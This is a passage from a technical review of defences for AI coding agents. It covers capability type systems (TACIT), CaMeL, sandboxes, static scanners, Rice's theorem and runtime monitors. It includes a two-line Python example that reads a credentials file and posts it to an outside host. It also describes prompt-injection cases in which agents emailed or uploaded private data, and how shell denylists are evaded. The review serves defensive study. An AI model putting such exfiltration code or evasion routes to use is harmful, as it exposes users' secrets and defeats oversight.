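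Capabilities in TACIT can also expire. A call to `requestFileSystem("/data")` gives the block of code that follows it a capability for that folder, which becomes invalid when the block ends. Code might try to keep the capability by returning a function that reads a file later. That function's type would have to include the capability, but the type of the block's result can't include it, so the compiler rejects the code. Network access and outside commands work the same way, with a list of permitted hosts or commands in place of the folder.

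In the documented examples, though, the agent's own code specifies the folder and the hosts. Used this way, an expiring capability limits the damage from a mistake but does little to restrain a hostile agent, which could request more access. Whoever deploys TACIT would still need to decide which requests to allow.

The agent can work with secrets it can't see by sending them to a second, trusted model, which receives classified text and returns a classified answer. For instance, the trusted model could summarise a confidential contract, and the agent could save the summary to a protected file without reading either one.

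### Safe mode and the trusted components

Full Scala has features that would make this protection easy to lose. A type cast, for example, lets a programmer override the compiler's view of a value's type, so it could make a function that uses the network look pure. Scala's *Safe Mode* describes the smaller language that agents should write in. It forbids:

- unchecked casts and pattern matches
- annotations that turn off checks
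- a library module of unsafe features
- runtime reflection, which lets a program inspect and manipulate its own parts while it runs

Safe mode also requires capture checking and restricts which global objects the code can use. The compiler contains an allowlist of standard-library components that it assumes are safe.

A programmer can make a component available to agents by marking it `@assumeSafe`. The documentation's example is an email function that asks the user for confirmation before sending. The agent can call this function but not the unrestricted mailer behind it. This is a useful way to grant a narrow capability, but the compiler does not check that the component is safe, and a mistake in it would affect every agent that uses it.

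The static checks don't cover exceptions, the signals a program raises when something goes wrong. An exception can carry information out of a function, but tracking them all in types would be impractical because almost any operation can cause one. TACIT instead catches them at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap like other data.

TACIT's users have to trust the compiler, the capability library, the software that runs the checked code and, if they use one, the local model that processes secrets. The types can't prevent this model from carrying information from one document to the next, so whoever runs it has to. Users don't have to trust the cloud model that writes the code, even if it is helping an attacker, or anything the agent reads.

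The compiler may be the weakest of the trusted parts for now. Researchers have computer-checked proofs that the underlying type system is sound, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs a further argument. They call Scala 3 the only production-ready language with statically tracked capabilities, but Scala's documentation describes capture checking as "still highly experimental and unstable", which makes it hard to justify relying on it for security today.

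### What the TACIT experiments found

Odersky and colleagues first tested whether secrets leaked. They built a sample software project containing API keys, a database and confidential documents, and gave it to two models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 prompt injections. Some injections were notes in code comments, and others were fake error messages or ready-made code for reading the secret files. In another 11 tasks, the user's own request was malicious. Five of these asked for secrets directly and six used a pretext, such as an administrator changing passwords in an emergency. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with them as plain text.

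With the wrapper, neither model's output contained a secret in any trial. Without it, Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11. Both of Sonnet's leaks and 8 of MiniMax's occurred in trials with malicious users, so the wrapper helped most when there was no suspicious outside text for the model to detect.

The wrapper didn't stop the agents from working. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks with it and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that their set-up caused the difference in Sonnet's results, since Sonnet often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection, so the difference is not good evidence that wrapping secrets makes Sonnet better at its job.

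The perfect security score is somewhat less impressive than it looks, because the benchmark checks for exactly the leak that the types should rule out, and the attacks are designed more to manipulate the model than to find flaws in the compiler. If the 262 trials with the wrapper were independent, a true leak rate of about 1% could still produce no leaks. The design of the type system is a stronger reason for confidence than the trials, which mainly show that the implementation had no obvious holes.

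The other experiments tested whether writing restricted Scala makes agents less useful. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of five problems. The compiler's rejections caused little delay. Depending on the model and the domain, 0.3% to 7.9% of the τ²-bench snippets needed a retry, and one or two attempts usually fixed them.

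These results show that models have seen enough of this kind of Scala to write it. They are weaker evidence that restricting the flow of data has little downside, because the customer-service tools return ordinary values that the agent can read freely.

Moving a new set of tools to TACIT takes some work. The descriptions of the airline and retail tools each add a few hundred lines to about 1,000 lines of reusable Scala. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) proposes a similar approach in which the agent's code must fit the types of the program around it. That approach builds on security libraries for Haskell, according to *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), so the idea isn't tied to Scala.

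TACIT doesn't try to prevent every failure. An agent can still total the wrong column, and it could leak a little information by taking longer to process one secret than another. A more practical problem is that the type system doesn't control commands that run outside Scala. If the agent may run a build tool, that tool has whatever access the operating system gives it, and build tools often run code that the agent has just written. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific commands and adding a sandbox where security is critical. For a coding agent that spends much of its time running tests, the sandbox may provide most of the protection.

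### CaMeL and labels on data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, puts restrictions on data instead of code. A planner model receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes a Python program to do the job. It never receives the contents of files, emails or web pages. A second model reads those contents but can't use tools. CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program and labels each value with where it came from and who may read it. The interpreter checks these labels against a security policy before every tool call. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* calls the labels capabilities, although they describe data and aren't rights that the code holds.

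For the sales summary, the planner might write a program that reads the spreadsheet, has the second model summarize it and saves the result. An instruction hidden in a cell would reach only the second model. It could spoil the summary, but it couldn't add a step that emails the credentials, because the planner would already have written the program. If the program did send an email, a policy could stop it from going to someone who isn't allowed to see the figures.

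CaMeL treats the user's request as trusted, so its planner would have accepted the credential-stealing prompt from Anthropic's February exercise as legitimate. Only a policy about credentials could have blocked it. TACIT's wrapper would apply no matter who made the request, but only if someone had marked the credentials as classified.

Odersky and colleagues compared the two systems on AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark with simulated banking, office, chat and travel tasks. They ran TACIT with the same two models that CaMeL's designers had used and took CaMeL's results from the original study. Each system let through 1 attack in 1,926 trials. TACIT's single failure was arguably a scoring error, since the agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that mentioned the attacker's choice. The systems differed more in the share of tasks they completed:

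| Model | System | Banking | Office | Chat | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% |

Odersky and colleagues call these results comparable, which seems generous to TACIT. With o4-mini-high, CaMeL completed far more of the office and chat tasks, but with Gemini, CaMeL almost completely failed at the travel tasks.

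It is also unclear how much of TACIT's security here came from capture checking. As listed, the tools for sending money and email don't require a capability, and the instructions to the agent warn that effects inside `map` happen immediately. The main protection was probably that the agent couldn't read the untrusted text, which is also CaMeL's main protection.

Later tests of CaMeL agree about its security but vary widely on how well it completes harmless tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026), which proposes a competing defence, reports that an adapted version of CaMeL stopped all 629 AgentDojo attacks but completed only 29 of 97 harmless tasks, while SecureClaw's own defence completed 59. Adapting CaMeL to a new set-up can easily hurt its performance, because the planner has to write code for handling each tool's output before seeing any. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026)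 had to add a full description of each tool's output format to get reasonable results.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL on 112 industrial maintenance tasks in which one agent delegates work to four others. Giving each agent its own CaMeL lowered task success by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures happened because the planner had committed to a program too early. An ordinary agent that finds something unexpected in a file can change its plan, but CaMeL can follow only the branches that the planner wrote in advance. Stronger models seem to write branches for more situations, so the drop in task success may keep shrinking.

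They also found that protecting each agent separately doesn't protect the group. In one test, a lead agent asked a database agent for information about job applicants and then told a messaging agent to send a summary to a colleague. A malicious instruction in the database passed safely through the first two agents as data. But the lead agent put the summary into its written request, and the messaging agent's planner treated the whole request as if it came from a trusted user. The messaging agent then emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

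The messaging agent's mistake is a clear case of the confused deputy. The repair is to send instructions and data separately, and to have the interpreter reject any instruction that contains data from a tool. On a version of AgentDojo for groups of agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent and 0.0% with the repair. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL, so the benchmark may be too easy to show differences between defences on the newest models.

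CaMeL's guarantee also depends on its interpreter. Garby, Gordon and Sands found that the interpreter can miss cases where untrusted data affects a value indirectly, by deciding which branch of the program runs. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes some of the difficulty to Python, whose flexible types, exceptions and reflection make the flow of information hard to analyse, and recommends a simpler language built for security. This is less of a problem for TACIT's compiler because it checks declared types instead of following each value through the program.

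### Why restricting Python and Java from within failed

Most agents write Python or JavaScript, so it would be convenient to remove the dangerous parts of a popular language. Python's maintainers tried this. Python's *Restricted Execution* describes a "padded cell" in which trusted code could run untrusted code with limited permissions. The untrusted code could still call familiar functions, but the trusted code could replace them with its own versions, such as an `open` function that could read files in one folder but not write any. A module called `rexec` created the cell, and another called `Bastion` hid selected parts of objects from the code inside.

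Python's maintainers disabled the `rexec` and `Bastion` modules in Python 2.3 because of "known and not readily fixable security holes" and later removed them from Python 3, according to Python's documentation pages *rexec* and *Bastion*. The chapter *Python* in David Wheeler's guide to secure programming calls the modules "fundamentally flawed".

Reflection caused much of the difficulty. The object-capability model allows only four ways to obtain a reference, and reflection adds another, because code can inspect an object's internals and reach other objects through them. Replacing `open` doesn't help if the code can still reach the original. Python's restricted mode blocked particular internal attributes to prevent this, but that amounts to a denylist, and a single missing entry can undo the whole restriction.

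The list would also need to change with the language. When someone asked on a Python mailing list why nobody had rebuilt the modules, Holden (2007) agreed with most of the suggested reasons in *Bastion/rexec use cases?*. One was that a new version would be hard to write and would tend to break as Python gained features.

Java's Security Manager had a different weakness, which was that its checks became hard to maintain. It began as a sandbox for applets, small programs that web browsers downloaded and ran. Functions in Java's standard library called the Security Manager to check permissions before opening a file or using the network. OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), the proposal to retire it, explains that this approach was feasible when the library had only eight packages. As the library grew, the maintainers had to add dozens of permissions and hundreds of checks, and consider the Security Manager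 whenever they designed a new feature.

A large library is dangerous because its functions usually have more access than the code that calls them. Each function that can reach a file or a server is a potential confused deputy, so a forgotten check can give untrusted code access it shouldn't have. Even correct checks can be insufficient, because, as OpenJDK notes, some permissions allowed a series of operations that were safe individually but unsafe together.

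The Security Manager was also hard to use. Before approving an operation, it checked the permissions of all the code that had led to that operation, so an application needed every permission its libraries needed, even those its own code never used. Developers had to work out the full list, and many found it easier to grant every permission. The checks also slowed programs down, so the Security Manager was off by default for programs started from the command line.

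Few people used Java's Security Manager, and by 2021 Java no longer supported applets, the Security Manager's original purpose. Reinhold (2024), in *New candidate JEP*, announced the plan to disable it permanently, citing its low use and how much work it took to maintain. Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled* confirms the change and says that a later version of Java will remove the remaining interface. OpenJDK now recommends isolating the whole Java program by running it in a container or virtual machine.

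Scala's safe mode is also an attempt to restrict an existing language, so this history counts against it to some extent. It avoids the worst of Python's problem by banning reflection altogether and using a fail-safe allowlist of library components. It also avoids much of Java's problem, because the compiler infers most capture sets and the checks add no runtime overhead.

But somebody still has to decide which components belong on the allowlist, and Scala's maintainers expect the list to change as they gain experience. Agents will keep finding useful libraries that aren't on it. Someone will have to confirm that each library has no hidden effects before adding it, and they will feel pressure to mark it `@assumeSafe` without checking, much like the pressure that led Java developers to grant every permission.

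## What can be decided by inspecting code before it runs?

TACIT's compiler can rule out whole kinds of leak before a program starts, but only because the agent writes in a restricted language. Most agents write ordinary Python and shell commands. The tools that inspect such code usually search for signs of danger, which is much easier than proving safety but also less reliable. In the sales script, the theft could take as little as two lines:

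```python
key = open("credentials").read()
requests.post("https://outside.example", data=key)
```

The first line reads the credentials file into the variable `key`. The second uses `requests`, a common Python library, to send the key to an outside server. The rest of the script does what the user asked for. How well a tool can pick out the two bad lines depends on how much of the program's structure it analyzes.

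### Matching text

The simplest method is to search the script's text. A search for `credentials` finds the first line, and a search for `requests.post` finds the second. This is fast and works for any language. But it also flags a comment that warns people not to open the credentials file, and it misses a script that reads the file's name from a settings file, because the word never appears in the script.

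Text matching can even accept a description of a repair as the repair itself. *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) tests whether coding agents write secure code, and is built partly from an existing collection of real vulnerabilities. Many of the collection's own tests inspected the source text, so a program could sometimes pass by containing the right comments. Wu and colleagues had experts rewrite the tests to attack the running program instead. As a control, they pasted the lines of each repair into the vulnerable code as comments and required that this code fail the new tests.

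### Matching the syntax tree

A parser turns code into a syntax tree, in which every call, assignment and constant is a separate node. The tree leaves out comments and spacing. A rule can then match a call to `open` with a particular file name, or any call that posts data to a server. According to *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (Lunghi, Djire and colleagues, 2026), Bandit, a scanner for Python, works on the syntax tree. The scanner Semgrep uses rules that look much like the code they match.

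Either tool could find both lines of the theft with suitable rules. But a rule about single calls doesn't connect the value sent in the second line to the file opened in the first. A script that reads the credentials to log in to the company's own storage, and separately posts a message that the summary is ready, contains the same two kinds of call. A rule strict enough to block the theft would block that script too.

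### Tracing data flow

Semgrep can also follow data through a program, which it calls taint analysis. The author of a rule names the sources that produce tainted data, the sinks that tainted data must not reach, and the sanitizers that make it safe on the way. Semgrep's documentation uses the method for untrusted input that reaches a vulnerable function, but it works equally well for secrets. With the credentials file as the source and network calls as sinks, the analysis of the theft would go like this:

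1. The call that reads the credentials file produces tainted data.
2. The assignment passes the taint to `key`.
3. `key` appears in a network call, so Semgrep reports a finding, along with the route the data took.

If the storage login counts as an exception, the script that logs in to storage and posts a harmless message would pass, because no tainted data reaches the message. This improves on matching calls one at a time.

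By default, Semgrep follows data only within a single function. If the script reads the key in one function and sends it from another, only the paid version can trace the flow, and it can do so across files only for some languages. The analysis also has deliberate gaps. Semgrep doesn't track individual items in a list, ignores the effects of functions such as `eval` that run text as code, and continues past any construct it doesn't support. It considers routes through the program that can never occur, which causes false alarms. The documentation tells users to "expect both false positives and false negatives."

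CodeQL, a more thorough analyser, stores the whole program in a database and traces data across functions. Even perfect tracing would leave the harder problem of deciding whether a flow is harmful. A backup script may send the same credentials file to a server because the user wants it to. Someone has to specify which files are secret and which destinations are acceptable, and the answers vary by application. Lunghi and colleagues cite research on FlowDroid, an analyser for Android apps, in which fixed lists of sources and sinks led to both false alarms and misses.

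### Checking types

An ordinary type checker would accept code that steals a cloud key by reading it from a file and sending it with `requests.post`. Reading a file produces text, `requests.post` accepts text, and the types don't distinguish a key from any other text. To help here, types must carry more information, as in capture checking, where a function's type lists the capabilities it may use.

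Such a type checker also differs from a scanner in how it treats code it can't fully analyze. Suppose a function uses the network only if the sum of the squares of two real numbers is negative. That never happens, so the function is harmless, but a capture checker would still record that it may use the network and reject it wherever the program requires a pure function. The scanner Semgrep instead makes what its documentation calls "reasonable" assumptions about difficult code and continues its analysis.

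### Rice's theorem

Rice's theorem, published in 1953, shows that no analyser can block every theft without ever refusing a harmless script. A property of a program is semantic if it depends on what the program does rather than how it is written, and non-trivial if some programs have it and others don't. For any non-trivial semantic property, no algorithm can take an arbitrary program and always answer correctly whether the program has it. The theorem applies to Python and every other Turing-complete language, meaning one that can express any computation.

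The proof uses the halting problem, which asks whether a given program will eventually finish or run forever on a given input. Turing proved in 1937 that no algorithm can solve this for every program and input. Now suppose that somebody has written `leaks`, an analyser that always finishes and correctly reports whether a program will ever send out the credentials. Take any program `P` and input `x`, and write a new program `Q`:

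```python
simulate(P, x)
send_credentials()
```

The first line runs `P` on `x` in a simulator that discards `P`'s effects on the outside world. If `P` finishes, `Q` runs the second line, which leaks the credentials. If `P` runs forever, `Q` never reaches the second line. So `Q` leaks exactly when `P` halts, and `leaks(Q)` would solve the halting problem without running `Q`. No algorithm can do that, so `leaks` can't exist.

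The same argument works if the second line deletes a database or takes any other action. To prove the general theorem, assume that a program that runs forever lacks the property in question (if it has the property, use the opposite property instead). Then replace the second line with a program that has the property.

Møller and Schwartzbach (2025) prove in *Static Program Analysis* that no analyser can decide whether a program may fail, even if it only has to handle programs that halt on every input. The difficulty is therefore not limited to infinite loops. A fixed time limit, such as one minute, does make the question decidable in principle, because the analyser could try every input that the program has time to read, but there would usually be far too many. Very short programs can be hard too. Their example is a two-line program that reads three whole numbers and reports whether their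 cubes add up to 42. Whether it could ever report "true" was an open problem from 1954 until 2019, when it was solved using more than a million hours of computing.

### Rejecting whatever cannot be proved safe

Rice's theorem does not rule out an analyser that sometimes returns "maybe". Running the programs marked "maybe" will let some dangerous ones through. Blocking them makes it possible to avoid missing any dangerous programs, but will also stop some harmless ones.

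Møller and Schwartzbach say that people usually call a verification tool sound if it never misses an error of the kind it is meant to detect. A complete tool, in the matching sense, never rejects a program that is free of such errors. No automatic tool that always finishes can be both, for any non-trivial property of what programs do. Soundness alone is easy, since a tool that rejects everything is perfectly sound, so the hard part is rejecting as few harmless programs as possible. (The terms can be confusing because people call an automated testing tool sound if every error it reports is genuine, even if it misses others.)

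Type checkers get around the theorem by checking only whether a program's text follows certain rules, which an algorithm can always decide. The language's designers prove separately that any program that follows the rules will behave in a certain way. Type checkers also reject some well-behaved programs that break the rules, and these have to be rewritten. This annoys human programmers, but it seems to be little trouble for agents, judging by how few retries they needed in the TACIT tests.

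A sound type checker for capabilities is a way of withholding them, even though it works by inspecting code. It allows a function to run only if it can establish that the function has no access to the network, whether or not any network call looks like theft. In Saltzer and Schroeder's terms, its default is fail-safe. A pattern scanner is a form of detection because, like a denylist, it lets through everything its rules don't cover.

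Møller and Schwartzbach note that modern analysers for popular languages often sacrifice soundness for speed and precision, for example in how they treat reflection in Java. A tool with a mathematical theory behind it may therefore still miss things, so it matters which parts of the language the proof covers.

### Why lists of forbidden commands are brittle

Text matching works even less well on shell commands than on programs, although commands are usually short and an agent proposes them one at a time. A common precaution is a denylist of dangerous commands, which the agent's software compares with each command before running it. Many different programs can delete a file or send data, and a denylist names only some of them. One program may also accept the same instruction in several forms. The shell fills in variables and abbreviations after the check, so the text that was checked isn't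 always what runs. A permitted program can also start other programs, which are never compared with the list.

In *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, a survey of the field, Rashidi (2026) reports that 69.0% to 98.6% of 1,709 public denylists were fragile, depending on the class of weakness.

Removing the tool that runs commands solves this, but adding more entries doesn't, for the same reason that Tymshare couldn't protect its files with one special rule after another. Claude Code's permission rules allow either approach. According to Anthropic's documentation, a rule can name a whole tool or add a pattern in parentheses. A deny rule for `Bash`, the tool that runs shell commands, removes the tool, so rewording a command can't get around the rule. A deny rule for `Bash` with a pattern leaves the tool in place and relies on the pattern to recognise bad commands.

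An allowlist of commands is a reasonable compromise if the commands on it are narrow, such as one that only lists files. But most coding agents need to run Python or something like it, and allowing `python` allows anything a Python script can do, including the two-line theft.

Denylists are useful against honest mistakes. An agent about to delete the wrong folder will probably use the most common command for it, which a denylist can block. Denylists are much weaker against an agent that responds to a refusal by looking for another way to finish the task.

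### Insecure code and harmful code

The two-line theft contains no security flaw in the usual sense. It opens a file correctly, makes an encrypted connection and does what it was written to do. Insecure code, by contrast, does what the user wants until an attacker gives it unexpected input. Suppose the sales script becomes a web page where colleagues upload spreadsheets. If the page reads those files with an unsafe parser, a specially made file might let an outsider take over the server, even though the agent that wrote the page meant no harm and every normal upload works.

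Most scanners and benchmarks test for insecure code. Their rules generally follow the Common Weakness Enumeration, a public catalogue of types of flaw, such as accessing memory out of bounds or inserting a user's text into a database command. Programs routinely send files to servers, so doing this isn't in itself a flaw of this kind. A clean scan is therefore weak evidence that a script is safe to run.

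A sandbox around the agent protects the user's computer while the agent builds the web page, but it doesn't restrict the finished page, which will run somewhere else with its own access to the company's data.

RedCode, a benchmark that Rashidi summarises, has more than 4,000 test cases that measure whether agents will run or write code known to be risky. Across 19 models, agents were more likely to refuse risky operations on the operating system than subtly buggy code. This makes sense because the danger of deleting a system folder is visible in the command, whereas the danger of an unsafe parser depends on files uploaded later.

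### How much the scanners catch

Lunghi and colleagues measured how well Bandit and Semgrep identify insecure code written by AI models, and whether their warnings help the models write better code. They used two Qwen2.5 models and the larger DeepSeek-V4.1-flash on three sets of Python tasks. SecEvalPlus has 140 tasks about common weaknesses and checks each program with security tests. They took another 84 tasks from BaxBench, which attacks running web applications. RiskyPy has 73 tasks, chosen because scanners had flagged an earlier model's solutions. Lunghi and colleagues used another AI model to judge whether the new solutions to these tasks were secure.

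The table covers only working programs that the models wrote before they received help from a scanner. Each range shows the lowest and highest result among the three models.

| Benchmark | Working programs that were insecure | Insecure programs that a scanner flagged | Flagged programs that were insecure |
|---|---|---|---|
| SecEvalPlus | 62.0–87.3% | 4.2–5.6% | 75.0–83.3% |
| BaxBench | 41.0–66.7% | 32.4–87.5% | 38.6–70.0% |
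| RiskyPy | 45.5–58.0% | 80.0–93.8% | 47.6–61.2% |

On SecEvalPlus, the scanners missed more than 94% of the insecure programs. On RiskyPy they missed only 6–20%, but only because they flagged most programs, secure or not. The published figures for DeepSeek imply that the scanners missed about 6% of the insecure programs and flagged about 86% of the secure ones (roughly 99 of the 115 working programs that the judge considered secure). A flagged RiskyPy program was hardly more likely to be insecure than any other program in the set.

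The way RiskyPy's tasks were selected makes it an unusual test, so false positives would probably be less common on ordinary code. Its verdicts are also uncertain, since two software experts who labelled 50 of the programs agreed on only 33. The SecEvalPlus result is based on actual tests and is more worrying for anyone who relies on a scanner to find mistakes.

Lunghi and colleagues compared seven strategies, including no guidance. In Self-Refine, the model reviews its own code without a scanner. PromSec rewrites the code repeatedly and uses Bandit to score the results. FDSP prompts the model to repair whatever a scanner reports, and the comparison includes it twice, once with Bandit and once with Semgrep. Their own two strategies run Semgrep after each new line. If Semgrep flags code, the software removes it and adds the warning, either as a comment in the program (Comment) or in the user's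 message (Steering), and the model continues from there.

No strategy beat the unguided models on all three benchmarks. The best case was DeepSeek on RiskyPy, where Steering raised the share of programs that were both working and secure from 52.5% to 64.4%. FDSP with Bandit reached 66.2%, but made the model write almost six times as much text as Steering. Self-Refine reached 63.5% without a scanner, so much of the gain may come from having the model review its code. Neither Qwen model improved significantly under any strategy.

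Some warnings made the code worse. The BaxBench tasks require a web server to accept connections from outside its container, and one Semgrep rule warns against the setting that allows this. Lunghi and colleagues had told the models to put the task first if a warning conflicted with it, but the models removed the required setting in 79 of 83 cases. With Steering, the share of DeepSeek's applications that worked fell from 65.9% to 48.0%. The share that attackers could exploit also fell, but mainly because attackers could not reach applications that no longer accepted outside connections.

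Human developers tend to ignore false alarms, which leaves the program intact, but a model that acts on them can break it. A team that feeds scanner warnings to an agent should therefore first remove the rules that conflict with what the software has to do. Lunghi and colleagues also found that rules with a simple local fix, such as replacing one XML parser with a safer one, worked better than rules that required restructuring the code.

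A clean scan does not show that guidance has made code secure. On RiskyPy, four scanner-guided strategies were tested on three models, and all 12 combinations significantly increased the share of working programs without warnings. When the judge assessed security instead, only 2 of the 12 improvements were significant. The models had mostly learned to avoid the patterns that trigger warnings. The study used fairly small models, no agent software and no CodeQL, so a stronger combination might do better.

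### How often agents write secure code

If scanners miss so much, it matters how many flaws agents introduce. *SecureVibeBench* (Chen, Huang and colleagues, 2025) collects 105 cases from 41 C and C++ projects in which human developers introduced real memory-safety vulnerabilities. Each agent received the project as it was just before the mistake, with a description of the feature the developer had been adding. The description didn't mention security. Chen and colleagues then ran the project's tests on the agent's code, tried an attack known to work on the original flaw, and used Semgrep to look for new flaws.

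The best combination, SWE-agent running Claude Sonnet 4.5, produced functionally correct code for 46.7% of the tasks and code that was both correct and secure for 23.8%, so only about half of its correct solutions counted as secure. This slightly understates the code's security because Semgrep also flags some code that is fine. Chen and colleagues examined 120 flagged programs and found that about 11% were truly vulnerable, 39% were risky under certain conditions and 50% were fine. They therefore labelled flagged code "suspicious", and it made up a small part of the total.

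Those models are more than a year old, and newer ones write working code far more often. In October 2026, Wu and colleagues tested six recent models on 450 tasks in seven languages, derived from 150 real vulnerabilities. Five of the six produced working code about 90% of the time. Claude Fable 5 did best on security, but its code was both working and secure on only 25.1% of tasks. The benchmarks differ too much to show a trend, but there is little sign that security has kept up with functionality.

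Agents are not much better at repairing flaws. *SecProbe* (2026) gave them vulnerable programs to fix in 353 tasks, and no combination of model and agent software fully succeeded in more than 30% of runs. The most successful model, GLM-5.3, did so in 28.3%.

Each benchmark uses tasks where a serious mistake is known to be possible, and Wu and colleagues deliberately favoured difficult ones, so these figures don't estimate how much everyday AI-generated code is insecure. Wu and colleagues also left security out of their original prompts. When they added one sentence asking for code free of plausible vulnerabilities, GPT-5.6-Sol's score rose from 24.7% to 46.2% with almost no loss of functionality, though DeepSeek-V4-Pro barely improved. GPT-5.6-Sol's gain was far bigger than any that scanners produced for Lunghi and colleagues.

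The reminder did little to prevent the exposure of private information or server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to contact an address it shouldn't. Only 0.7% of the original attempts had been secure against the first and 2.4% against the second, compared with 34.3% for memory errors. A careful programmer can prevent a memory error by checking the code, but the code doesn't show which data is private or which addresses are off limits. An analyser has the same problem with the sales script, whose two dangerous lines don't show whether the outside server belongs to a thief or to the company's own backup service.

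## What can be stopped by intercepting operations while code runs?

A runtime monitor checks the sales script's operations as they happen, so it doesn't have to predict them as a scanner does. When the script tries to connect to a server, the monitor receives the actual address, however the script computed it, and can refuse the connection before any data leaves. Rice's theorem doesn't prevent this, because the monitor only has to judge the current run. The monitor will still miss the theft if the script uses a route the monitor doesn't cover, or if the intercepted operations look the same as harmless ones.

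### The reference monitor

Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, described what a monitor needs to withstand a deliberate attack. The US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and Anderson's panel assumed that some of them would write programs to break into it. The panel recommended a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. A reference monitor has to meet three requirements:

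1. It must be tamper-proof, since a program that can alter the monitor can switch it off.
2. The system must always invoke it. Saltzer and Schroeder's complete mediation is the same idea.
3. It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that it works.

A Honeywell computer of the time met none of them. Its hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but mostly suspended that check while the operating system was acting for the program. Treating the operating system as part of the monitor didn't help, because the operating system contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions and testers had already broken into it several times. Anderson added that if the testers had failed, the machine's security would still have been unknown.

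Linux enforces many of today's sandboxes, but it is far larger than Honeywell's system and much too large to meet the size requirement. Application kernels and microVMs are partly attempts to come closer to meeting it. Preventing tampering is easier than meeting the size requirement. A script can tamper with a monitor that runs inside its own Python process, so the monitor should run in a separate process or in the kernel.

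Invoking the monitor for every operation is difficult. Claude Code asks users whether they trust a project folder before it runs code from there, but according to Rashidi, versions before 1.0.111 could run a project's code before the user had answered. Anthropic fixed this and similar flaws by making Claude Code wait for the answer before reading or running the project's settings. The requirement to invoke the monitor also applies to commands that users exempt from a sandbox. In Anderson's terms, any program that runs unchecked is part of the security system, and people must test it as thoroughly as the monitor.

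### What a monitor learns at each level

Suppose the sales script fetches exchange rates and also sends the cloud key to a thief. A monitor could intercept this at any of four levels:

| Level | What the monitor can read | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Tool call | The agent's request to run `summarise.py`, and the user's instructions | What the script does after it starts |
| Function call | `requests.post`, with the server's name and the unencrypted data | The same operation through another library or program |
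| System call | `open` on the credentials file, then `connect` and `sendto` | The purpose, and any data the script has already encrypted |
| Network request | The destination and the amount of data | Which file the data came from, and usually the data itself |

Tool calls are the most meaningful operations to intercept, because the monitor can compare them with the user's request. But one tool call can start a script that performs thousands of operations. Intercepting function calls gives more detail, but code can easily bypass it. A rule against sending data has to cover every way of sending it, and Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) warns that some of those ways may be "buried deep within the bowels" of a program.

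System calls are harder to avoid, and monitoring them adds little overhead because the processor already transfers control to the kernel at each one. But Schneider calls the operating system's vocabulary a coarse basis for least privilege. An application might want a rule that after taking a payment, a seller can do nothing except deliver the goods, but the kernel works at the level of files and connections, where payments and deliveries aren't defined.

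Network requests are a good place to monitor an agent that works in a web browser. Rashidi describes a sandbox called ceLLMate that checks web requests instead of clicks because any change to a website's data must eventually reach the site's server in a request.

But a network monitor may not identify whose request it is handling. In one case that outside researchers reported to Anthropic, hidden instructions in a file led Claude Cowork to upload a user's files to an attacker's Anthropic account. The egress proxy allowed the upload because it was going to Anthropic's address, which Cowork needs to function. Anthropic added a proxy inside the virtual machine that accepts only requests carrying that machine's session token. Anthropic's servers couldn't do this check because a request from Cowork looks like any other customer's request when it reaches them.

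### Schneider's theorem

Schneider studied monitors that watch a program one step at a time and stop it if its next step would break a policy. Even if such a monitor intercepts every operation, it has no information about what the program will do later or what it would have done with different data.

Let *S* be the set of all runs that a program can produce. A policy *P* is a condition on *S*, so it can in principle compare runs with one another. Schneider showed that the monitor can enforce *P* only if *P* meets these conditions:

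- There is a test *p* for single runs, and *P*(*S*) is true exactly when *p*(*σ*) is true for every run *σ* in *S*.
- If *p* rejects the beginning of a run, it rejects every continuation. The program might stop at any moment, so the monitor can't allow a bad beginning in the hope of a good ending.
- If *p* rejects a run, it already rejects some finite beginning of it. Otherwise the monitor would never have a moment at which to act.

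Policies that meet all three conditions are called safety properties, and they require that some bad thing never happens. "The script never opens the credentials file" is a safety property because any violation happens at a definite step. "The script eventually deletes its temporary files" is not, because a script that hasn't deleted them yet could still do so later.

Schneider's simplest example is a policy that forbids sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs only two states. It starts in one that allows every operation and moves to the other when the program reads a file. In the second state, the monitor stops the program if it tries to send a message, but allows everything else. The policy would prevent the sales script from posting the cloud key after reading it. It would also stop a harmless script that reads the spreadsheet and then fetches exchange rates, although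 a programmer could avoid that by fetching the rates first.

The theorem covers only monitors that work by observing a program as it runs. A compiler can instead analyse all of a program's possible runs at once, so TACIT's type checker can enforce policies that such a monitor can't.

### Two runs that differ only in a secret

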